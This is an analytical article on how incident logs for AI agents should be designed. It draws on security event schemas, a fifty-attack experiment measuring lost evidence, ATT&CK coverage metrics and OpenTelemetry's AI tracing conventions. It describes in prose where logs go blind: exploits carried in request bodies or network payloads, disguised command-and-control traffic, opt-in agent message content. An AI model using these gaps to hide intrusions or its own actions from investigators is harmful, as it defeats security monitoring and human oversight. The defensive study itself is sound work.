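# What AI incident logs must record: lessons from coverage gaps in security event schemas

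## Security logs, shared schemas and AI agents

An incident log is all the evidence an organisation keeps so that investigators can work out how a system caused harm. It differs from an incident report, which is the selected account that a regulator or the public receives. Keeping such logs for AI systems is a new practice. Companies now deploy AI agents, which use tools to pursue a task over many steps. When an agent deletes the wrong files or sends data to the wrong place, investigators have to reconstruct what it did from whatever the surrounding software happened to record.

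Computer security has dealt with a similar problem for decades. Security teams collect logs from many products, convert them into a shared format and search the result for signs of attack. Widely used formats include Splunk's Common Information Model (CIM), the Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF) and the Elastic Common Schema (ECS). *Beyond Collection* (Holeman, Hastings and Vaidyan, 2026) measured how much evidence of an attack survives conversion into each format. AI agents raise the same question of which facts a log must hold for somebody to explain an incident from it.

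Telemetry is the data a system emits about its own activity. An event is one recorded occurrence, such as a login, a started process or an agent's use of a tool. An event schema is an agreed list of event types and fields, and normalisation converts raw logs into that schema.

### One login, from raw record to alert

Splunk's *Authentication Field Mapping* includes a sample record of a login to the Amazon Web Services (AWS) web console. The record gives the event name as `ConsoleLogin`, the result as `Success`, the user as `example_user` and the time as 23:06:26 UTC on 21 February 2020. `MFAUsed: No` means that the user supplied no second proof of identity, such as a code from a phone. The `sourceIPAddress` field contains the network address the login came from, 4.14.104.185.

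Other providers record the same fact under other names. Google Cloud's record of a successful login has `ipAddress`, while its record of a failed one has `callerIp`. Microsoft 365 records the address twice, as `ActorIpAddress` and `ClientIP`. An analyst looking for every login from one address would have to know all these names and learn more for each new product. Normalisation replaces them with a single name, although that name differs between schemas.

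| Where the login appears | Field holding the source address |
|---|---|
| Google Cloud, raw | `ipAddress` or `callerIp` |
| Microsoft 365, raw | `ActorIpAddress` and `ClientIP` |
| AWS, raw | `sourceIPAddress` |
| CIM | `src` |
| OCSF | `src_endpoint.ip` |
| ECS | `source.ip` |

To turn the AWS record into an OCSF event, the converting software first picks an event type. Tenzir, a company that builds security data pipelines, publishes a copy of the OCSF 1.7.0 definitions, in which logins belong to the class Authentication, number 3002. A new logon is activity 1 within that class. The software multiplies the class number by 100 and adds the activity number, which gives the event type 300201. It then converts the time into milliseconds since the start of 1970 and moves the remaining details into their fields. In abridged form the result is:

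```
class_uid:        3002            (Authentication)
activity_id:      1               (Logon)
type_uid:         300201
status_id:        1               (Success)
time:             1582326386000
user.name:        example_user
src_endpoint.ip:  4.14.104.185
is_mfa:           false
```

A detection rule is a stored condition that software applies to incoming events, raising an alert when one or more match. A rule against password guessing, written for CIM, might raise an alert when a single value of `src` has failed logins for twenty different values of `user` within ten minutes, followed by a success. The same rule covers AWS, Google and Microsoft, and its writer does not need to know their raw field names. In a simple search from a copy of Elastic's documentation hosted by Wikimedia, `source.ip` replaces five field names joined by "or". However, the rule now depends on the schema. The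 ready-made detections in Splunk's products use CIM, so the company supplies an add-on, described in Splunk's *Overview of the OCSF CIM add-on*, that translates OCSF events into CIM. According to Splunk, customers who do not use the add-on have to create detections for OCSF data themselves.

Many rules match indicators, which are observable details that point to an attack, such as an address that attackers have used before, the hash (a short digital fingerprint) of a malicious file, or a telltale command. Each OCSF event has an optional list, called `observables`, that gathers such details in one place. OCSF's documentation explains that an analyst can then search every event for a set of suspect addresses without knowing which of the many address fields to check. Traces also differ in how much they prove. A high-fidelity signature, such as a web request containing a command to open a connection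 back to the sender, shows an attack almost by itself. A login from an unfamiliar address is a low-fidelity signature, which only adds suspicion, because the user may be an employee who is traveling.

Shared schemas standardize field names more easily than the meaning of the values in them. In Splunk's three successful logins, the CIM field `authentication_method` receives "password" from Google, "1" from Microsoft and "No" from AWS, where "No" means that the user did not supply a second factor. The field `user_agent`, meant for the browser or program that made the request, receives `admin#reports#activity` from Google, a label for the type of record. Google's `is_suspicious` flag has no counterpart in the mapping. A search on `src` works well across these events, but a search on `authentication_method` would compare values that describe different things.

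### Who maintains the schemas, and what they make compulsory

Splunk owns CIM and distributes it as an add-on to its log-search software. CIM has one data model for each domain, such as authentication or network traffic, and each model is a fairly flat list of fields and tags. Splunk describes the content as the "least common denominator" of a domain. The software applies the common field names when somebody searches and leaves the original log unchanged. An event enters a data model only if it has the right tag, which for logins is `authentication`.

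A consortium of security vendors and other contributors develops OCSF. The project joined the Linux Foundation on 19 November 2024, according to OCSF, and has a steering committee and a group of maintainers. Its structure has more layers than CIM's. A dictionary defines every attribute, and event classes such as Authentication select attributes from it. Each class belongs to exactly one category, which for Authentication is Identity & Access Management. Objects group the attributes of a thing such as a user, a device or a file. Profiles add optional attributes, such as details of the host computer, to many classes at once. Tenzir counts 83 event classes, 170 objects and 12 profiles in version 1.7.0.

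Elastic, the company behind the Elasticsearch database, maintains ECS as an open-source specification and takes changes through its public code repository. ECS groups fields with a common prefix into field sets, such as `source.ip`, `source.port` and `source.domain`. In April 2023, Elastic and OpenTelemetry, an open-source project for collecting telemetry, announced a plan to merge ECS with OpenTelemetry's naming rules. According to OpenTelemetry's announcement, the result would be a single schema maintained by OpenTelemetry. Holeman and colleagues instead describe OpenTelemetry's rules as merging into ECS. The merger remains incomplete, and Elastic's *OTel Alignment Overview* still compares two separately numbered specifications.

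Each schema also has requirement levels, which state how far a field is compulsory, and here the same words carry different obligations.

OCSF has the strictest definitions. *Introduction to the Framework and Schema* (Agbabian, 2024) explains that readers of an event can rely on its required attributes being present. If the source never supplied the information, the converter fills in a default, usually "Unknown", so a required attribute may hold nothing useful. Recommended attributes should have a value where possible, but validation software does not check them individually. For some classes, it does check that at least one attribute from a named group has a value. Optional attributes add context when the source provides more detail. In the login class, `user` is required, and `raw_data`, the original record, is optional.

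In CIM, "recommended" means that the developers who write the conversions do their best to fill the field, and Splunk's *Authentication* warns that an event without the recommended fields is not very useful. "Required" means only that developers must map the field if they use a particular Splunk tool to test for compatibility. For logins, the required fields are `action`, `app` and `user`. The source address, `src`, is only recommended, and `authentication_method` is optional. Holeman and colleagues write that logs conforming to CIM must include the required fields, which is stronger than Splunk's wording.

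ECS requires very few fields. Elastic's *Guidelines and best practices* requires a timestamp in every event, and its *ECS Fields* requires a field for the schema version. The remaining fields are either core or extended. Core fields are common to most uses, and teams fill them first when they start converting their logs. Extended fields serve narrower purposes and change more often. These labels describe how widely useful a field is, and users decide whether to fill it. In Elastic's *Source fields*, `source.ip` is core, while `source.address`, which preserves the address as the original log gave it, is extended, even though the same page advises always filling it when the source is ambiguous.

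A login event can thus conform to CIM or ECS and still lack the login's source address. Conformity means that software can read the event, but it does not guarantee that the event holds enough information to answer a given question, since different questions require different information.

### Detection and post-incident analysis

Agbabian describes a security analyst who "writes rules against the events and searches events during investigation". These two jobs require different things from a log.

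Detection means finding out whether something bad is happening. It requires a distinguishing trace early enough for someone to act, but it can still work when most traces are lost. If an intrusion leaves six traces and normalisation destroys five, the sixth may still set off the alert. Investigators analysing the incident afterwards need to know what happened, who or what caused it, why, and how far it went, and any of the five lost traces may have held one of those answers.

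A failed Windows login illustrates the difference. In an example from Google Cloud's *Collect OCSF logs*, the normalised fields show that a logon for the account Administrator failed, and when. A rule that counts failures needs nothing more. The example's `unmapped` section holds details that the converter had no standard field for, including the Windows code 0xC000006A. That code means that the account exists but the password was wrong; another code means that the account does not exist. Over a few hundred failures, investigators can use these codes to tell an attacker who is guessing account names from one who already has a list of real accounts, and a stolen list would change what they investigate. But `unmapped` and `raw_data` are both optional in OCSF, so a converter can discard them and still produce a valid event.

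How much this matters depends on whether the original log is kept. CIM leaves the raw log unchanged, so an analyst can return to it for as long as the organisation keeps it. When Splunk's software converts incoming data to OCSF, it can overwrite the original text, although the customer can configure it to keep a copy.

Summarising has a similar effect. For efficiency, OCSF allows a converter to merge many events of the same type into one, with a count, a start time and an end time. A rule with a threshold of twenty failed logins may work as well on the merged event as on the separate ones. But the merged event omits the order and spacing of the failures, which are evidence of whether a script or a person entered the passwords.

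Identifying who acted often requires linking events. On Google Cloud, a user can request short-lived credentials for a service account, an account that belongs to a program instead of a person. In Splunk's example of such a request, CIM records the requester in `src_user` and the service account in `user`. If the service account later copies a database, an alert on the copying is correct even if no one can find the earlier request, but identifying the person responsible requires that request or an equivalent link. The same is true whenever an AI agent uses credentials that a person has lent it.

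To establish how far an incident went, investigators need evidence that detection rarely uses. For example, to conclude that an intruder never reached the payroll system, they need a complete log of that system for the whole period, showing no intrusion. Such a log triggers no detection rules, so it is an obvious candidate for deletion when storage runs short.

A log can also support a near-perfect reconstruction of an incident without having warned anyone about it. This could happen if an organisation archives a full copy of its network traffic but searches it only after a customer complains.

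### One step of an agent's work

A language model takes in text and produces text. It becomes an agent when ordinary software, called a scaffold, assembles its input, runs its tools and filters its output. Suppose an engineer lets an agent read files and run commands on one server, and asks it to find out why last night's backup failed.

The scaffold first assembles the context, which is everything the model will read at this step. The context typically contains the operator's standing instructions, the engineer's request, descriptions of the available tools and the results of earlier steps. It may also include notes from memory, a store that outlasts the single run. The model usually retains nothing between steps, so the scaffold must supply the relevant history each time. The model then generates text. Often it first produces a reasoning trace, in which it works towards a decision, and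 then a tool call, which is a request for software to act for it. The call includes arguments, such as a command to show free disk space. Nothing has happened on the server yet. The scaffold checks the request against the agent's permissions, perhaps asks a human to approve it, and passes it to the tool. The tool runs the command and returns a result, which shows a full disk. The scaffold adds the result to the context and the loop repeats until the model gives a final answer or the scaffold stops the run.

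Each of these points offers an opportunity to make a record.

| Point in the loop | What a record could hold |
|---|---|
| Scaffold assembles the context | The exact text sent to the model, the origin of each part, the model version and its settings |
| Model generates its output | The reasoning trace, where the provider makes it available, and the tool call as the model wrote it |
| Scaffold handles the request | The permissions in force, any human approval, and whether the scaffold allowed, changed or blocked the call |
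| Tool acts | The command as executed, the account it ran under, and the server's own events, such as a started process |
| Result returns | The full result, and the version of it that the scaffold placed in the context |
| Run continues or ends | Changes to memory, and the reason for stopping |

The two items in some of these pairs can differ, even though they look redundant. A scaffold may shorten a long result before it reaches the model, and an investigator with only the full version could blame the model for ignoring a warning it never received. A filter may also rewrite a command after the model requests it but before it runs.

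The disk-space command also leaves traces in two places. The scaffold's log has a tool call, and the server's operating system may log a started process, an ordinary security event that all three schemas can represent. If both records carry a common identifier, an investigator can join them immediately. Otherwise the investigator has to match them by time, which becomes difficult when many agents share one server and one account.

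Engineers arrange such records mainly as transcripts or spans. A transcript records one agent run in order, including its messages, reasoning traces, tool calls and results. A span records one timed operation and links to the operation that caused it, so a set of spans forms a tree showing which step led to which. Security schemas have begun to cover this material. lmodel's *Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF)*, a machine-readable version of a development release, lists a profile for AI operations, and Elastic's *Generative AI fields now available in ECS* announces similar additions.

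## What three security schemas missed in fifty attacks

In an experiment published in May 2026, Holeman and colleagues carried out fifty attacks and compared the raw logs with the normalised ones.

*SETC* (Holeman, Hastings and Vaidyan, 2024) introduced Security Exploit Telemetry Collection, a tool for recording attacks, and reported a small pilot that preceded the larger experiment. The pilot covered six flaws in web software, with CIM as the only schema. The researchers searched the 16 resulting log events by hand for text from the attacks and found it for three of the six. In the other three, the attacker's commands were in a part of the web request that CIM leaves out. The larger experiment covers more kinds of software and all three schemas, and also measures how much of the weaker evidence survives.

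### The attacks and the logs

SETC runs each attack inside containers, isolated software environments that behave like small separate computers. One container hosts a vulnerable program, another attacks it, and others record what happens. If the attack fails, SETC tries again. When it succeeds, SETC collects the logs, converts them into each schema and destroys the containers. A configuration file describes every attack, so other researchers can repeat the series or rerun it with different logging.

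All fifty flaws allow remote code execution, meaning an attacker elsewhere on the network can make the target run commands. Forty are in web software, and the other ten are in services such as file sharing, email, chat, remote login and databases. The flaws date from 2005 to 2024. The attacks used modules from Metasploit, a widely used collection of ready-made exploits. Two modules appear twice in the published list, so the fifty entries represent 48 different modules.

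Every attack went through the same three phases, which the researchers took from MITRE ATT&CK, a public catalogue of attackers' methods maintained by the American non-profit MITRE:

- **Initial access:** the attacker sends the target a message that exploits the flaw.
- **Execution:** the target runs the attacker's commands, which usually install or start a second program.
- **Command and control:** the second program connects back to the attacker, who can then direct the machine.

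Three kinds of logs cover these phases. Web logs record requests to a web server, including the address and some headers (short labelled lines at the start of a request). Process logs show which programs ran, under which account and with which instructions. Network logs list connections between machines. SETC stored the raw telemetry and converted it into CIM 6.0.3, OCSF 1.6.0 and ECS 9.0.0.

The analysis took six steps. The researchers:

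1. labelled every event with the flaw it belonged to, using the start and end times of each attack;
2. read the source code of each exploit to establish which traces it should leave, and over which protocol;
3. searched the raw and normalised logs by hand for high-fidelity signatures of each phase;
4. gave the same logs to a language model, Claude Opus 4, which listed the low-fidelity signatures;
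5. checked the model's reports by hand, noted the errors and generated new reports until they found no more;
6. compared the raw logs with the normalised ones and calculated two scores.

### Two scores, worked through for Shellshock

The effectiveness score is the share of signatures that survive normalisation:

$$\text{effectiveness score} = \frac{\text{signatures in the normalised logs}}{\text{signatures in the raw logs}} \times 100$$

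The detection rate is the share of attacks for which the normalised logs contain a high-fidelity signature of every phase:

$$\text{detection rate} = \frac{\text{attacks with all three phases visible}}{\text{all attacks}} \times 100$$

The detection result for a single attack is either true or false. It is false if there is no evidence of one of the three phases, even if the evidence of the other two is overwhelming.

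The researchers illustrate both scores with Shellshock, a 2014 flaw in Bash, the program that interprets typed commands on many Linux systems. Some web servers pass parts of a request to Bash as variables, and vulnerable versions of Bash ran any commands hidden there. In the test, the attacker placed commands in the User-Agent header, which normally identifies the browser and its version. The commands wrote a small program into a temporary folder under a random name and started it. The program connected to the attacker's machine on port 4444.

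Claude found 16 signatures, 12 of which concerned the three phases. Some were weak, such as an unusually long User-Agent header, a large data transfer, or a connection that never closed. The table shows how many of the 12 each schema preserved.

| Schema | Initial access | Execution | Command and control | Total | Effectiveness |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIM | 3 of 3 | 4 of 4 | 2 of 5 | 9 of 12 | 75% |
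| OCSF | 3 of 3 | 3 of 4 | 2 of 5 | 8 of 12 | 66% |
| ECS | 3 of 3 | 3 of 4 | 2 of 5 | 8 of 12 | 66% |

OCSF and ECS each kept eight of the twelve signatures, or 66.7%, which the researchers round down. They looked for the commands in the User-Agent header, the start of the attacker's program and the outgoing connection to port 4444, and concluded that all three schemas still gave enough visibility of every phase of the chain.

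### Results for all fifty attacks

Across the fifty attacks, CIM preserved 63% of the signatures, OCSF 58% and ECS 57%. All three had a detection rate of 20%, and their rates also matched in every phase.

| Phase | CIM: signatures preserved | OCSF | ECS | Attacks with the phase visible, same for all three |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Initial access | 67% (161 of 242) | 60% (145) | 60% (146) | 26% (13 of 50) |
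| Execution | 73% (185 of 254) | 70% (179) | 69% (174) | 76% (38 of 50) |
| Command and control | 50% (122 of 246) | 45% (110) | 43% (107) | 90% (45 of 50) |
| Whole chain | 63% (468 of 743) | 58% (434) | 57% (427) | 20% (10 of 50) |

The researchers report a total of 743, but their counts for the three phases add up to 742. The difference does not affect the percentages.

Command and control has the lowest effectiveness score but the highest detection rate, because effectiveness is an average over all traces, while detection needs only one strong trace to survive. The attacks left about five command-and-control signatures each, and even CIM preserved only half of them. But network records consist mainly of addresses and ports, so the preserved signatures were usually enough to show the target connecting to the attacker. For Shellshock, two of the five signatures were enough to detect command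 and control.

Initial access shows the reverse pattern. CIM preserved two-thirds of the entry signatures but kept a decisive one in only 13 attacks. The contrast is greatest for the ten attacks on services other than websites, where OCSF preserved 29 of 51 entry signatures but revealed the entry in none of the attacks. The effectiveness score weights every signature equally, so the size of a request counts as much as the malicious command inside it.

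Although the detection rate was only 20%, at least 45 of the 50 attacks left a strong trace that could have set off an alarm. Evidence of how the attacker got in was missing most often. Execution was visible in 38 attacks and command and control in 45, so at least 33 attacks showed both. Only ten of those also showed the entry, so at least 23 of the 40 incomplete chains lacked only the entry. In those cases, investigators could see that a strange program had started and where it had connected, but they would still have to find out which flaw to repair.

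Holeman and colleagues conclude that process logs are the most valuable of the three sources. These logs may record a program that an attacker starts, however the attacker got in. They were also compact, averaging 15.3 events per attack, compared with 20 for web logs and 29 for network logs. The researchers credit process logs with both the 76% for execution and the 90% for command and control. But their procedure accepts either a process trace or a network trace as evidence of command and control. They do not report how many of the 45 cases depended on each, so the evidence for the value of process logs is clearer for execution.

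### Missing request bodies and network payloads

Most of the missing entry evidence is absent because ordinary web logs record a request's address and some headers but omit its body, a separate block after the headers. GET requests usually send data in the address, but POST requests, which login forms and file uploads typically use, usually send it in the body.

Eight of the forty web attacks used GET, alone or with POST, and the entry was visible in all eight. The other 32 used only POST. In 27 of these (67.5% of all the web attacks), the normalised logs contained no decisive trace of the entry. The remaining five presumably had telltale text in the address or headers. The pilot included a case of this kind, in which a request's address led out of the web server's folders to the system's command interpreter, and CIM preserved the address.

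The phrase "completely undetectable", which Holeman and colleagues use for the 27 attacks, applies only to how the attackers got in. Command and control was visible in 36 of the 40 web attacks, so it must have been visible in at least 23 of these 27.

None of the three schemas makes the request body a required or recommended field, but they differ in whether they have a place for it at all:

| Schema | Place for the request body |
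|---|---|
| CIM | No standard field |
| OCSF | Only a field for its length |
| ECS | A field for the full text, at the "extended" level |

The web fields in Splunk's *Common Information Model Add-on Manual* for the version tested include the address, query string and cookie, but not the request body. For OCSF, lmodel's *Class: HttpRequest* mentions body content in its description of a web request, but the only body attribute it lists is `body_length`. The optional attribute `args`, for arguments sent with the request, is defined loosely enough that some converters might put body data there. For OCSF 1.4.0, an older release, Tenzir lists even the length as optional. Elastic's *HTTP fields* defines `http.request.body.content` as the full request body. MITRE's own data model also has a field for the body.

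The remedy therefore depends on the schema. ECS users can fill an existing field, while CIM or OCSF users would normally have to add a custom field or keep the raw record. Either way, someone has to decide to collect the body. According to Holeman and colleagues, logging standards leave it out because it typically contains sensitive or private data. A login request, for example, may contain the user's password. Telemetry standards for AI systems similarly make message content opt-in.

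Holeman and colleagues suggest that software could learn to select safe and useful parts of the data that logs now exclude, but they have not tested this. Researchers could test it fairly easily with SETC by adding a body field and repeating the same 27 attacks. They would also need ordinary web traffic to measure how many passwords and private messages the new field captured along with the exploits.

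In *Logging and Telemetry Gap Identification of Remote Vulnerability Exploitation*, the dissertation behind the experiment, Holeman (2025) attributes the missing web evidence to headers as well as bodies. The Shellshock exploit was visible because it used the User-Agent header, which the normalised logs preserved. An exploit in a header without its own field could disappear in the same way as one in a body.

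Network records have a similar gap. They record a connection's addresses, ports, times and data volumes but omit the payload, the content the two machines exchanged. An attack on a file server or a database may therefore look like any other connection. In all ten attacks on services other than websites, the evidence of entry was in the payload, so the network records did not show it.

The explanation for the zero out of ten result makes it more convincing than the count alone. If a signature exists only in the payload and the record excludes payloads, testing more attacks of the same kind would give the same result. The count alone is weak evidence, because even if a quarter of all such attacks left visible entry traces, a random set of ten would include none about 6% of the time.

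### Why CIM preserved more

CIM's lead over OCSF comes entirely from the web attacks. CIM preserved 377 of the 589 signatures for those attacks, compared with 343 for OCSF and 342 for ECS. Half of CIM's 34 additional signatures over OCSF concerned initial access. For the other services, CIM and OCSF each preserved 91 of 153 signatures, and ECS preserved 85.

Holeman and colleagues attribute CIM's lead to its larger number of required fields, which capture details such as data sizes and categories. Splunk's list of web fields supports this, since it requires the number of bytes in each direction and the length of the User-Agent header, at least for developers who use Splunk's compatibility test. An overlong User-Agent header was one of the weak signatures in the Shellshock example. In OCSF, request length is optional, and in ECS, all request-size fields are classed as extended.

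The sample CIM record from the pilot has only a dash in `category`, a field that CIM requires. It also has a meaningless four-letter string where the request method, such as GET or POST, should be. An analyst might well find that string suspicious, but a stricter converter that accepted only known methods would have removed it.

The researchers describe their comparison as limited to required fields, but SETC's converters must have filled in many more for ECS. ECS requires only the timestamp and the schema version, which could not have preserved 57% of the signatures. The paper does not list the extra fields. The scores therefore measure SETC's versions of the three schemas, and a different converter for the same schema could produce higher or lower scores.

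Holeman and colleagues accept that optional or custom fields could give all three schemas equal coverage. CIM's practical advantage is that its default fields prompt developers to record more. A team that chose its fields carefully would have little reason to switch schemas for a five-point difference.

Decisions about what to collect can make a much larger difference. For *Measuring Attack Observability in Cloud Telemetry Logs*, Dhooghe, Park and colleagues (2026) carried out 35 kinds of attack from the ATT&CK catalogue on Amazon's, Google's and Microsoft's cloud platforms. They ran each scenario ten times with the attack and ten times without it, then compared the logs. With default settings, the logs reflected 45% to 48% of the attacks. Switching on additional logging raised this to between 65% and 88%, depending on the platform. Amazon's storage service, for example, records individual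 file deletions only if the customer turns on that logging.

These percentages are not directly comparable with Holeman's. A difference between two sets of logs shows only that an attack affected them, which is a lower standard than a trace that identifies each phase. But if a platform never records an event, no schema can preserve it.

### Limits of the experiment

The fifty attacks were uniform by design. Where possible, the researchers configured Metasploit to connect back to the attacker on port 4444, and they did not try to hide anything. This makes the schemas easier to compare, because each is applied to the same attack. It also makes command and control easier to see than it would often be in practice, because the attack always aimed at such a connection and the researchers knew its port and destination in advance. According to the guide that accompanies the tool's code, hackgnar's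 *SETC*, the tool by default even uses port 4444 to decide whether an exploit has succeeded. Investigators of a real intrusion don't know the port or destination at the start, and an attacker can choose a port that ordinary web traffic uses.

The containers also had no ordinary users. On a working server, an outgoing connection is one among thousands, so a trace that is visible in the experiment might escape notice. Holeman and colleagues point out that the lack of normal activity could also lead the experiment to understate detection. Security teams often detect an attack because it departs from a machine's usual behaviour, and a log with only weak signatures may be enough for that. The experiment could not measure this kind of detection.

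The sample was also limited to Linux targets running in containers and exploits available in Metasploit. The researchers chose flaws that fitted their attack chain and for which a vulnerable system was easy to obtain, so the percentages are not estimates for attacks in general. They stopped at command and control and did not study how an intruder gains further privileges or moves to other machines. Those activities leave different traces, so the three schemas might rank differently on them.

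Some losses may have occurred before normalisation. According to the tool's guide, SETC captures network traffic, a monitoring program called Zeek turns the capture into structured logs, and SETC converts those logs into each schema. If Zeek omits a detail, it is missing from every schema. The guide also describes the basic process logs as two snapshots, one taken before the exploit and one after, so a command that started and finished in between would appear in neither. An optional program, Falco, records processes continuously, but the paper does not state whether the researchers used it. Snapshots could account for some of the 12 attacks in which execution was not visible. This affects the detection rate, because its denominator includes all attacks, even any whose traces were missing from the raw logs. Gaps in a shared source could also explain why the three schemas produced identical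 results.

The effectiveness scores have a different weakness. They depend on a list that Claude Opus 4 drew up, and Holeman and colleagues report numerous errors and hallucinations. In the Shellshock example, Claude credited Zeek with complete coverage of execution, although Zeek monitors only network traffic and cannot detect a program starting on the target. This error distorted the totals. After manual correction, Zeek's coverage of execution was 0%. Claude Opus 4 dates from 2025, so these errors are a poor guide to current models, but they affected this study's data.

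Manual reviewers can remove false signatures more easily than they can decide what counts as one signature. The Shellshock list includes Bash starting processes under the web server's account, processes running under the account `www-data`, and relationships between parent and child processes. On many Linux systems `www-data` is the web server's account, so these three entries could describe largely the same fact. A schema that loses the account name might lose one point or two, depending on whether the list separates the first two entries. The scores for OCSF and ECS differ by only seven signatures out of more than 740. The paper includes no test of how much the scores would change if a second model or analyst made the list.

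These weaknesses hardly affect the request-body result. Holeman and colleagues identified the decisive signatures by hand from the exploit code, and the schemas' published definitions confirm that none of the three requires or recommends recording the request body. The ranking of the schemas is much less certain than this result.

### ATT&CK coverage as a measure of security

Detection coverage depends on the set of attacks used to measure it. Holeman and colleagues built their own set, whereas security companies usually take theirs from the ATT&CK catalogue. ATT&CK describes attackers' behaviour at three levels: tactics, which are goals such as stealing data; techniques, which are general methods of reaching those goals; and procedures, which are the concrete actions that analysts have seen in real attacks. A product usually counts as covering a technique if at least one of its detection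 rules is labelled with that technique.

Virkud, Inam and colleagues (2024), in *How does Endpoint Detection use the MITRE ATT&CK Framework?*, examined whether coverage in this sense measures security well. They collected 2,251 detection rules from Carbon Black, Splunk and Elastic as they stood in October 2022, when ATT&CK had 191 techniques. Carbon Black covered 55% of the techniques, Splunk 52% and Elastic 48%.

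Many of the rules behind these figures have little practical effect. Splunk and Elastic give each rule a risk score, which helps analysts decide which alerts to read first. When Virkud and colleagues counted only high-risk rules, coverage fell to 25% for Splunk and 26% for Elastic. A vendor can therefore raise its coverage by adding rules that customers will seldom act on. Sigma, a public collection to which anyone can contribute, reached 79% coverage, but this also fell when the researchers excluded the less critical rules.

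Complete coverage would not necessarily be desirable either, because vendors could cover some techniques only by writing rules that do not work. Fifty-three of the techniques had no rule in any of the three products. Virkud and colleagues examined the descriptions of these techniques and found that 21 had no effective method of detection, often because a rule would raise too many false alarms. Eight involved activity on other organisations' platforms, such as an attacker reading about a company's staff on social media, which software on the company's own computers cannot observe.

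The labels are also inconsistent. The researchers found 37 specific threats, such as a named piece of malware, for which at least two of the products had rules. For 19 of them, no two products agreed on a single technique. All the products agreed completely on only one threat. Some of the disagreement is reasonable, because one piece of malware can do many things and two companies may watch for different ones. But the products also label the same behaviour differently. Elastic and Splunk have nearly identical rules for suspicious use of `nslookup`, a Windows program that looks up internet addresses. Elastic labels this command and control, while Splunk labels it data theft. An analyst's conclusion about the attacker's goal could therefore depend on which product they use.

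When Virkud and colleagues showed MITRE their findings, one staff member replied that inconsistent labels might not be a problem and that the diversity could even be useful. The researchers largely accept this for experienced analysts, and it is a fair defence of ATT&CK as a vocabulary for describing attacks. It is less convincing when coverage is used as a metric, because a percentage means little if companies count the same rule under different headings. MITRE itself advises users not to treat the techniques as a checklist, but a company that assesses cyber risk told the researchers that its customers read 90% coverage as "90% secure".

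Holeman and colleagues' detection rate avoids some of these problems because they carried out attacks and looked for the traces instead of counting labels. However, at least one of their labels is still ambiguous. They call the execution phase "Exploitation for Client Execution", which in ATT&CK refers to flaws in client programs such as browsers, but all fifty of their targets were servers.

Virkud and colleagues raise a more serious objection to both kinds of percentage. Attackers can carry out one technique through many procedures, and a rule or test usually covers only a few of them. The 90% for command and control comes largely from one procedure, a direct connection back to the attacker on port 4444, repeated against different software. Hiding the same traffic in ordinary requests to a popular website is also command and control, but a record of addresses and ports might show nothing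 unusual.

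## What AI telemetry standards record by default

The web logs in the fifty-attack experiment omitted request bodies, which held most of the evidence of how the attackers got in. The main telemetry standard for AI systems, OpenTelemetry's conventions for generative AI, also omits message content unless somebody switches it on. OpenTelemetry is the open-source project whose naming rules Elastic plans to merge with ECS. Its conventions for generative AI define which spans an application should produce and which attributes, or named fields, each span should have. The code that creates the spans, called instrumentation, may come from OpenTelemetry, the maker of an agent framework or the company that runs the agent.

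### Spans for models, agents, workflows and tools

OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* covers single operations. A model call produces a span named after the operation and the model, such as `chat gpt-4`. Holloran (2026) writes in *Tracing LLM Calls with OpenTelemetry* that the span should also cover automatic retries, so a call that fails twice and then succeeds appears as one long call. Each tool run gets its own span, named `execute_tool` followed by the tool's name. A search of a document store gets a retrieval span.

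OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* adds spans for larger units of work. An `invoke_agent` span covers one invocation of an agent, with separate versions for agents on a remote service and agents inside the application. An `invoke_workflow` span covers a process that coordinates several agents. Only frameworks that can distinguish a workflow from an agent should produce it. CrewAI, which groups agents into "crews", should produce it, but ADK should not, because its coordinating agents look like any other agent. A missing workflow span therefore does not prove that an agent worked alone. *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026) lists further operations for planning, memory and the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way of connecting models to tools.

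Each span records its own identifier and, unless it is the first, its parent's identifier. In the example trace in OpenTelemetry's *Inside the LLM Call*, one `invoke_agent` span is the parent of a `chat` span for every model call and an `execute_tool` span for every tool call. Because a model call and the tool call it triggered are siblings, the parent link shows that the tool ran during this invocation, but not which model call triggered it. The tool call's identifier could link the two, but on the model's side it is part of the output message, which instrumentation omits by default. Investigators then have to match the calls by time, which is easy if the agent does one thing at a time and harder if several model calls overlap.

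If a tool runs on another machine, the request has to include the identifiers. The MCP conventions define how, but Wang cautions that not every MCP implementation follows them.

### A standard still in development

OpenTelemetry's specification gives the status of its generative AI conventions as "Development". In the table for model calls, the only stable attributes are the error type and the server's address and port, none of which is specific to AI. Some blogs describe the conventions as more settled than they are. For example, CallSphere's *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions for AI Agents in 2026* (2026) states that the rules for model calls left experimental status early in the year.

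In May 2026, OpenTelemetry (2026) created a separate repository for the conventions, and the old pages now redirect there. Wang found no official release in it as of 21 August. On 4 December, Holloran reported that everything in it still had Development status. Greptime (2026) found no public timeline for a stable version but considers the conventions a reasonable basis for new software because the core concepts have settled.

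The attribute names are still changing. The attribute for input written to a provider's cache is `gen_ai.usage.cache_creation.input_tokens` in OpenTelemetry's earlier text and `gen_ai.usage.cache_write.input_tokens` in Holloran's account. OpenTelemetry also says existing instrumentation should keep producing the names from version 1.36 or earlier until a user asks for the new ones. A company with several AI products may therefore have both sets of names in its logs, and a search for one set will miss the records that use the other.

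Many libraries also depart from the conventions. Groves (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI in the wild*, compared more than a dozen of them. Groves works for the monitoring company Datadog and presents the ranking as a personal one, but the faults it lists are specific:

- Langfuse and OpenInference replace the standard attribute names with their own.
- Spring AI uses the right names but stores every value as text, including token counts.
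- OpenLIT attaches tool calls to the parent span instead of giving each one a span.
- OpenTelemetry's own Python instrumentation still produces, by default, a schema derived from version 1.28.

A mismatched name usually causes no error message. According to Groves, the dashboard shows zero. An investigator could easily take that zero as evidence that nothing happened, when the data is in the log under another name.

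### Required, recommended and opt-in attributes

OpenTelemetry assigns each attribute one of four requirement levels. Instrumentation must fill required attributes, and it must fill conditionally required ones when the stated condition holds. It should normally fill recommended attributes, and it fills opt-in attributes only if the user asks for them. The table gives the levels of the attributes that matter most to an investigator. Token counts measure length in tokens, the short pieces of text that a model reads and writes.

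| Information | Attribute | Requirement level |
|---|---|---|
| Type of operation | `gen_ai.operation.name` | Required |
| Provider of the model | `gen_ai.provider.name` | Required for model calls |
| Model requested | `gen_ai.request.model` | Conditionally required, if available |
| Model that responded | `gen_ai.response.model` | Recommended |
| Token counts | `gen_ai.usage.input_tokens` and `gen_ai.usage.output_tokens` | Recommended |
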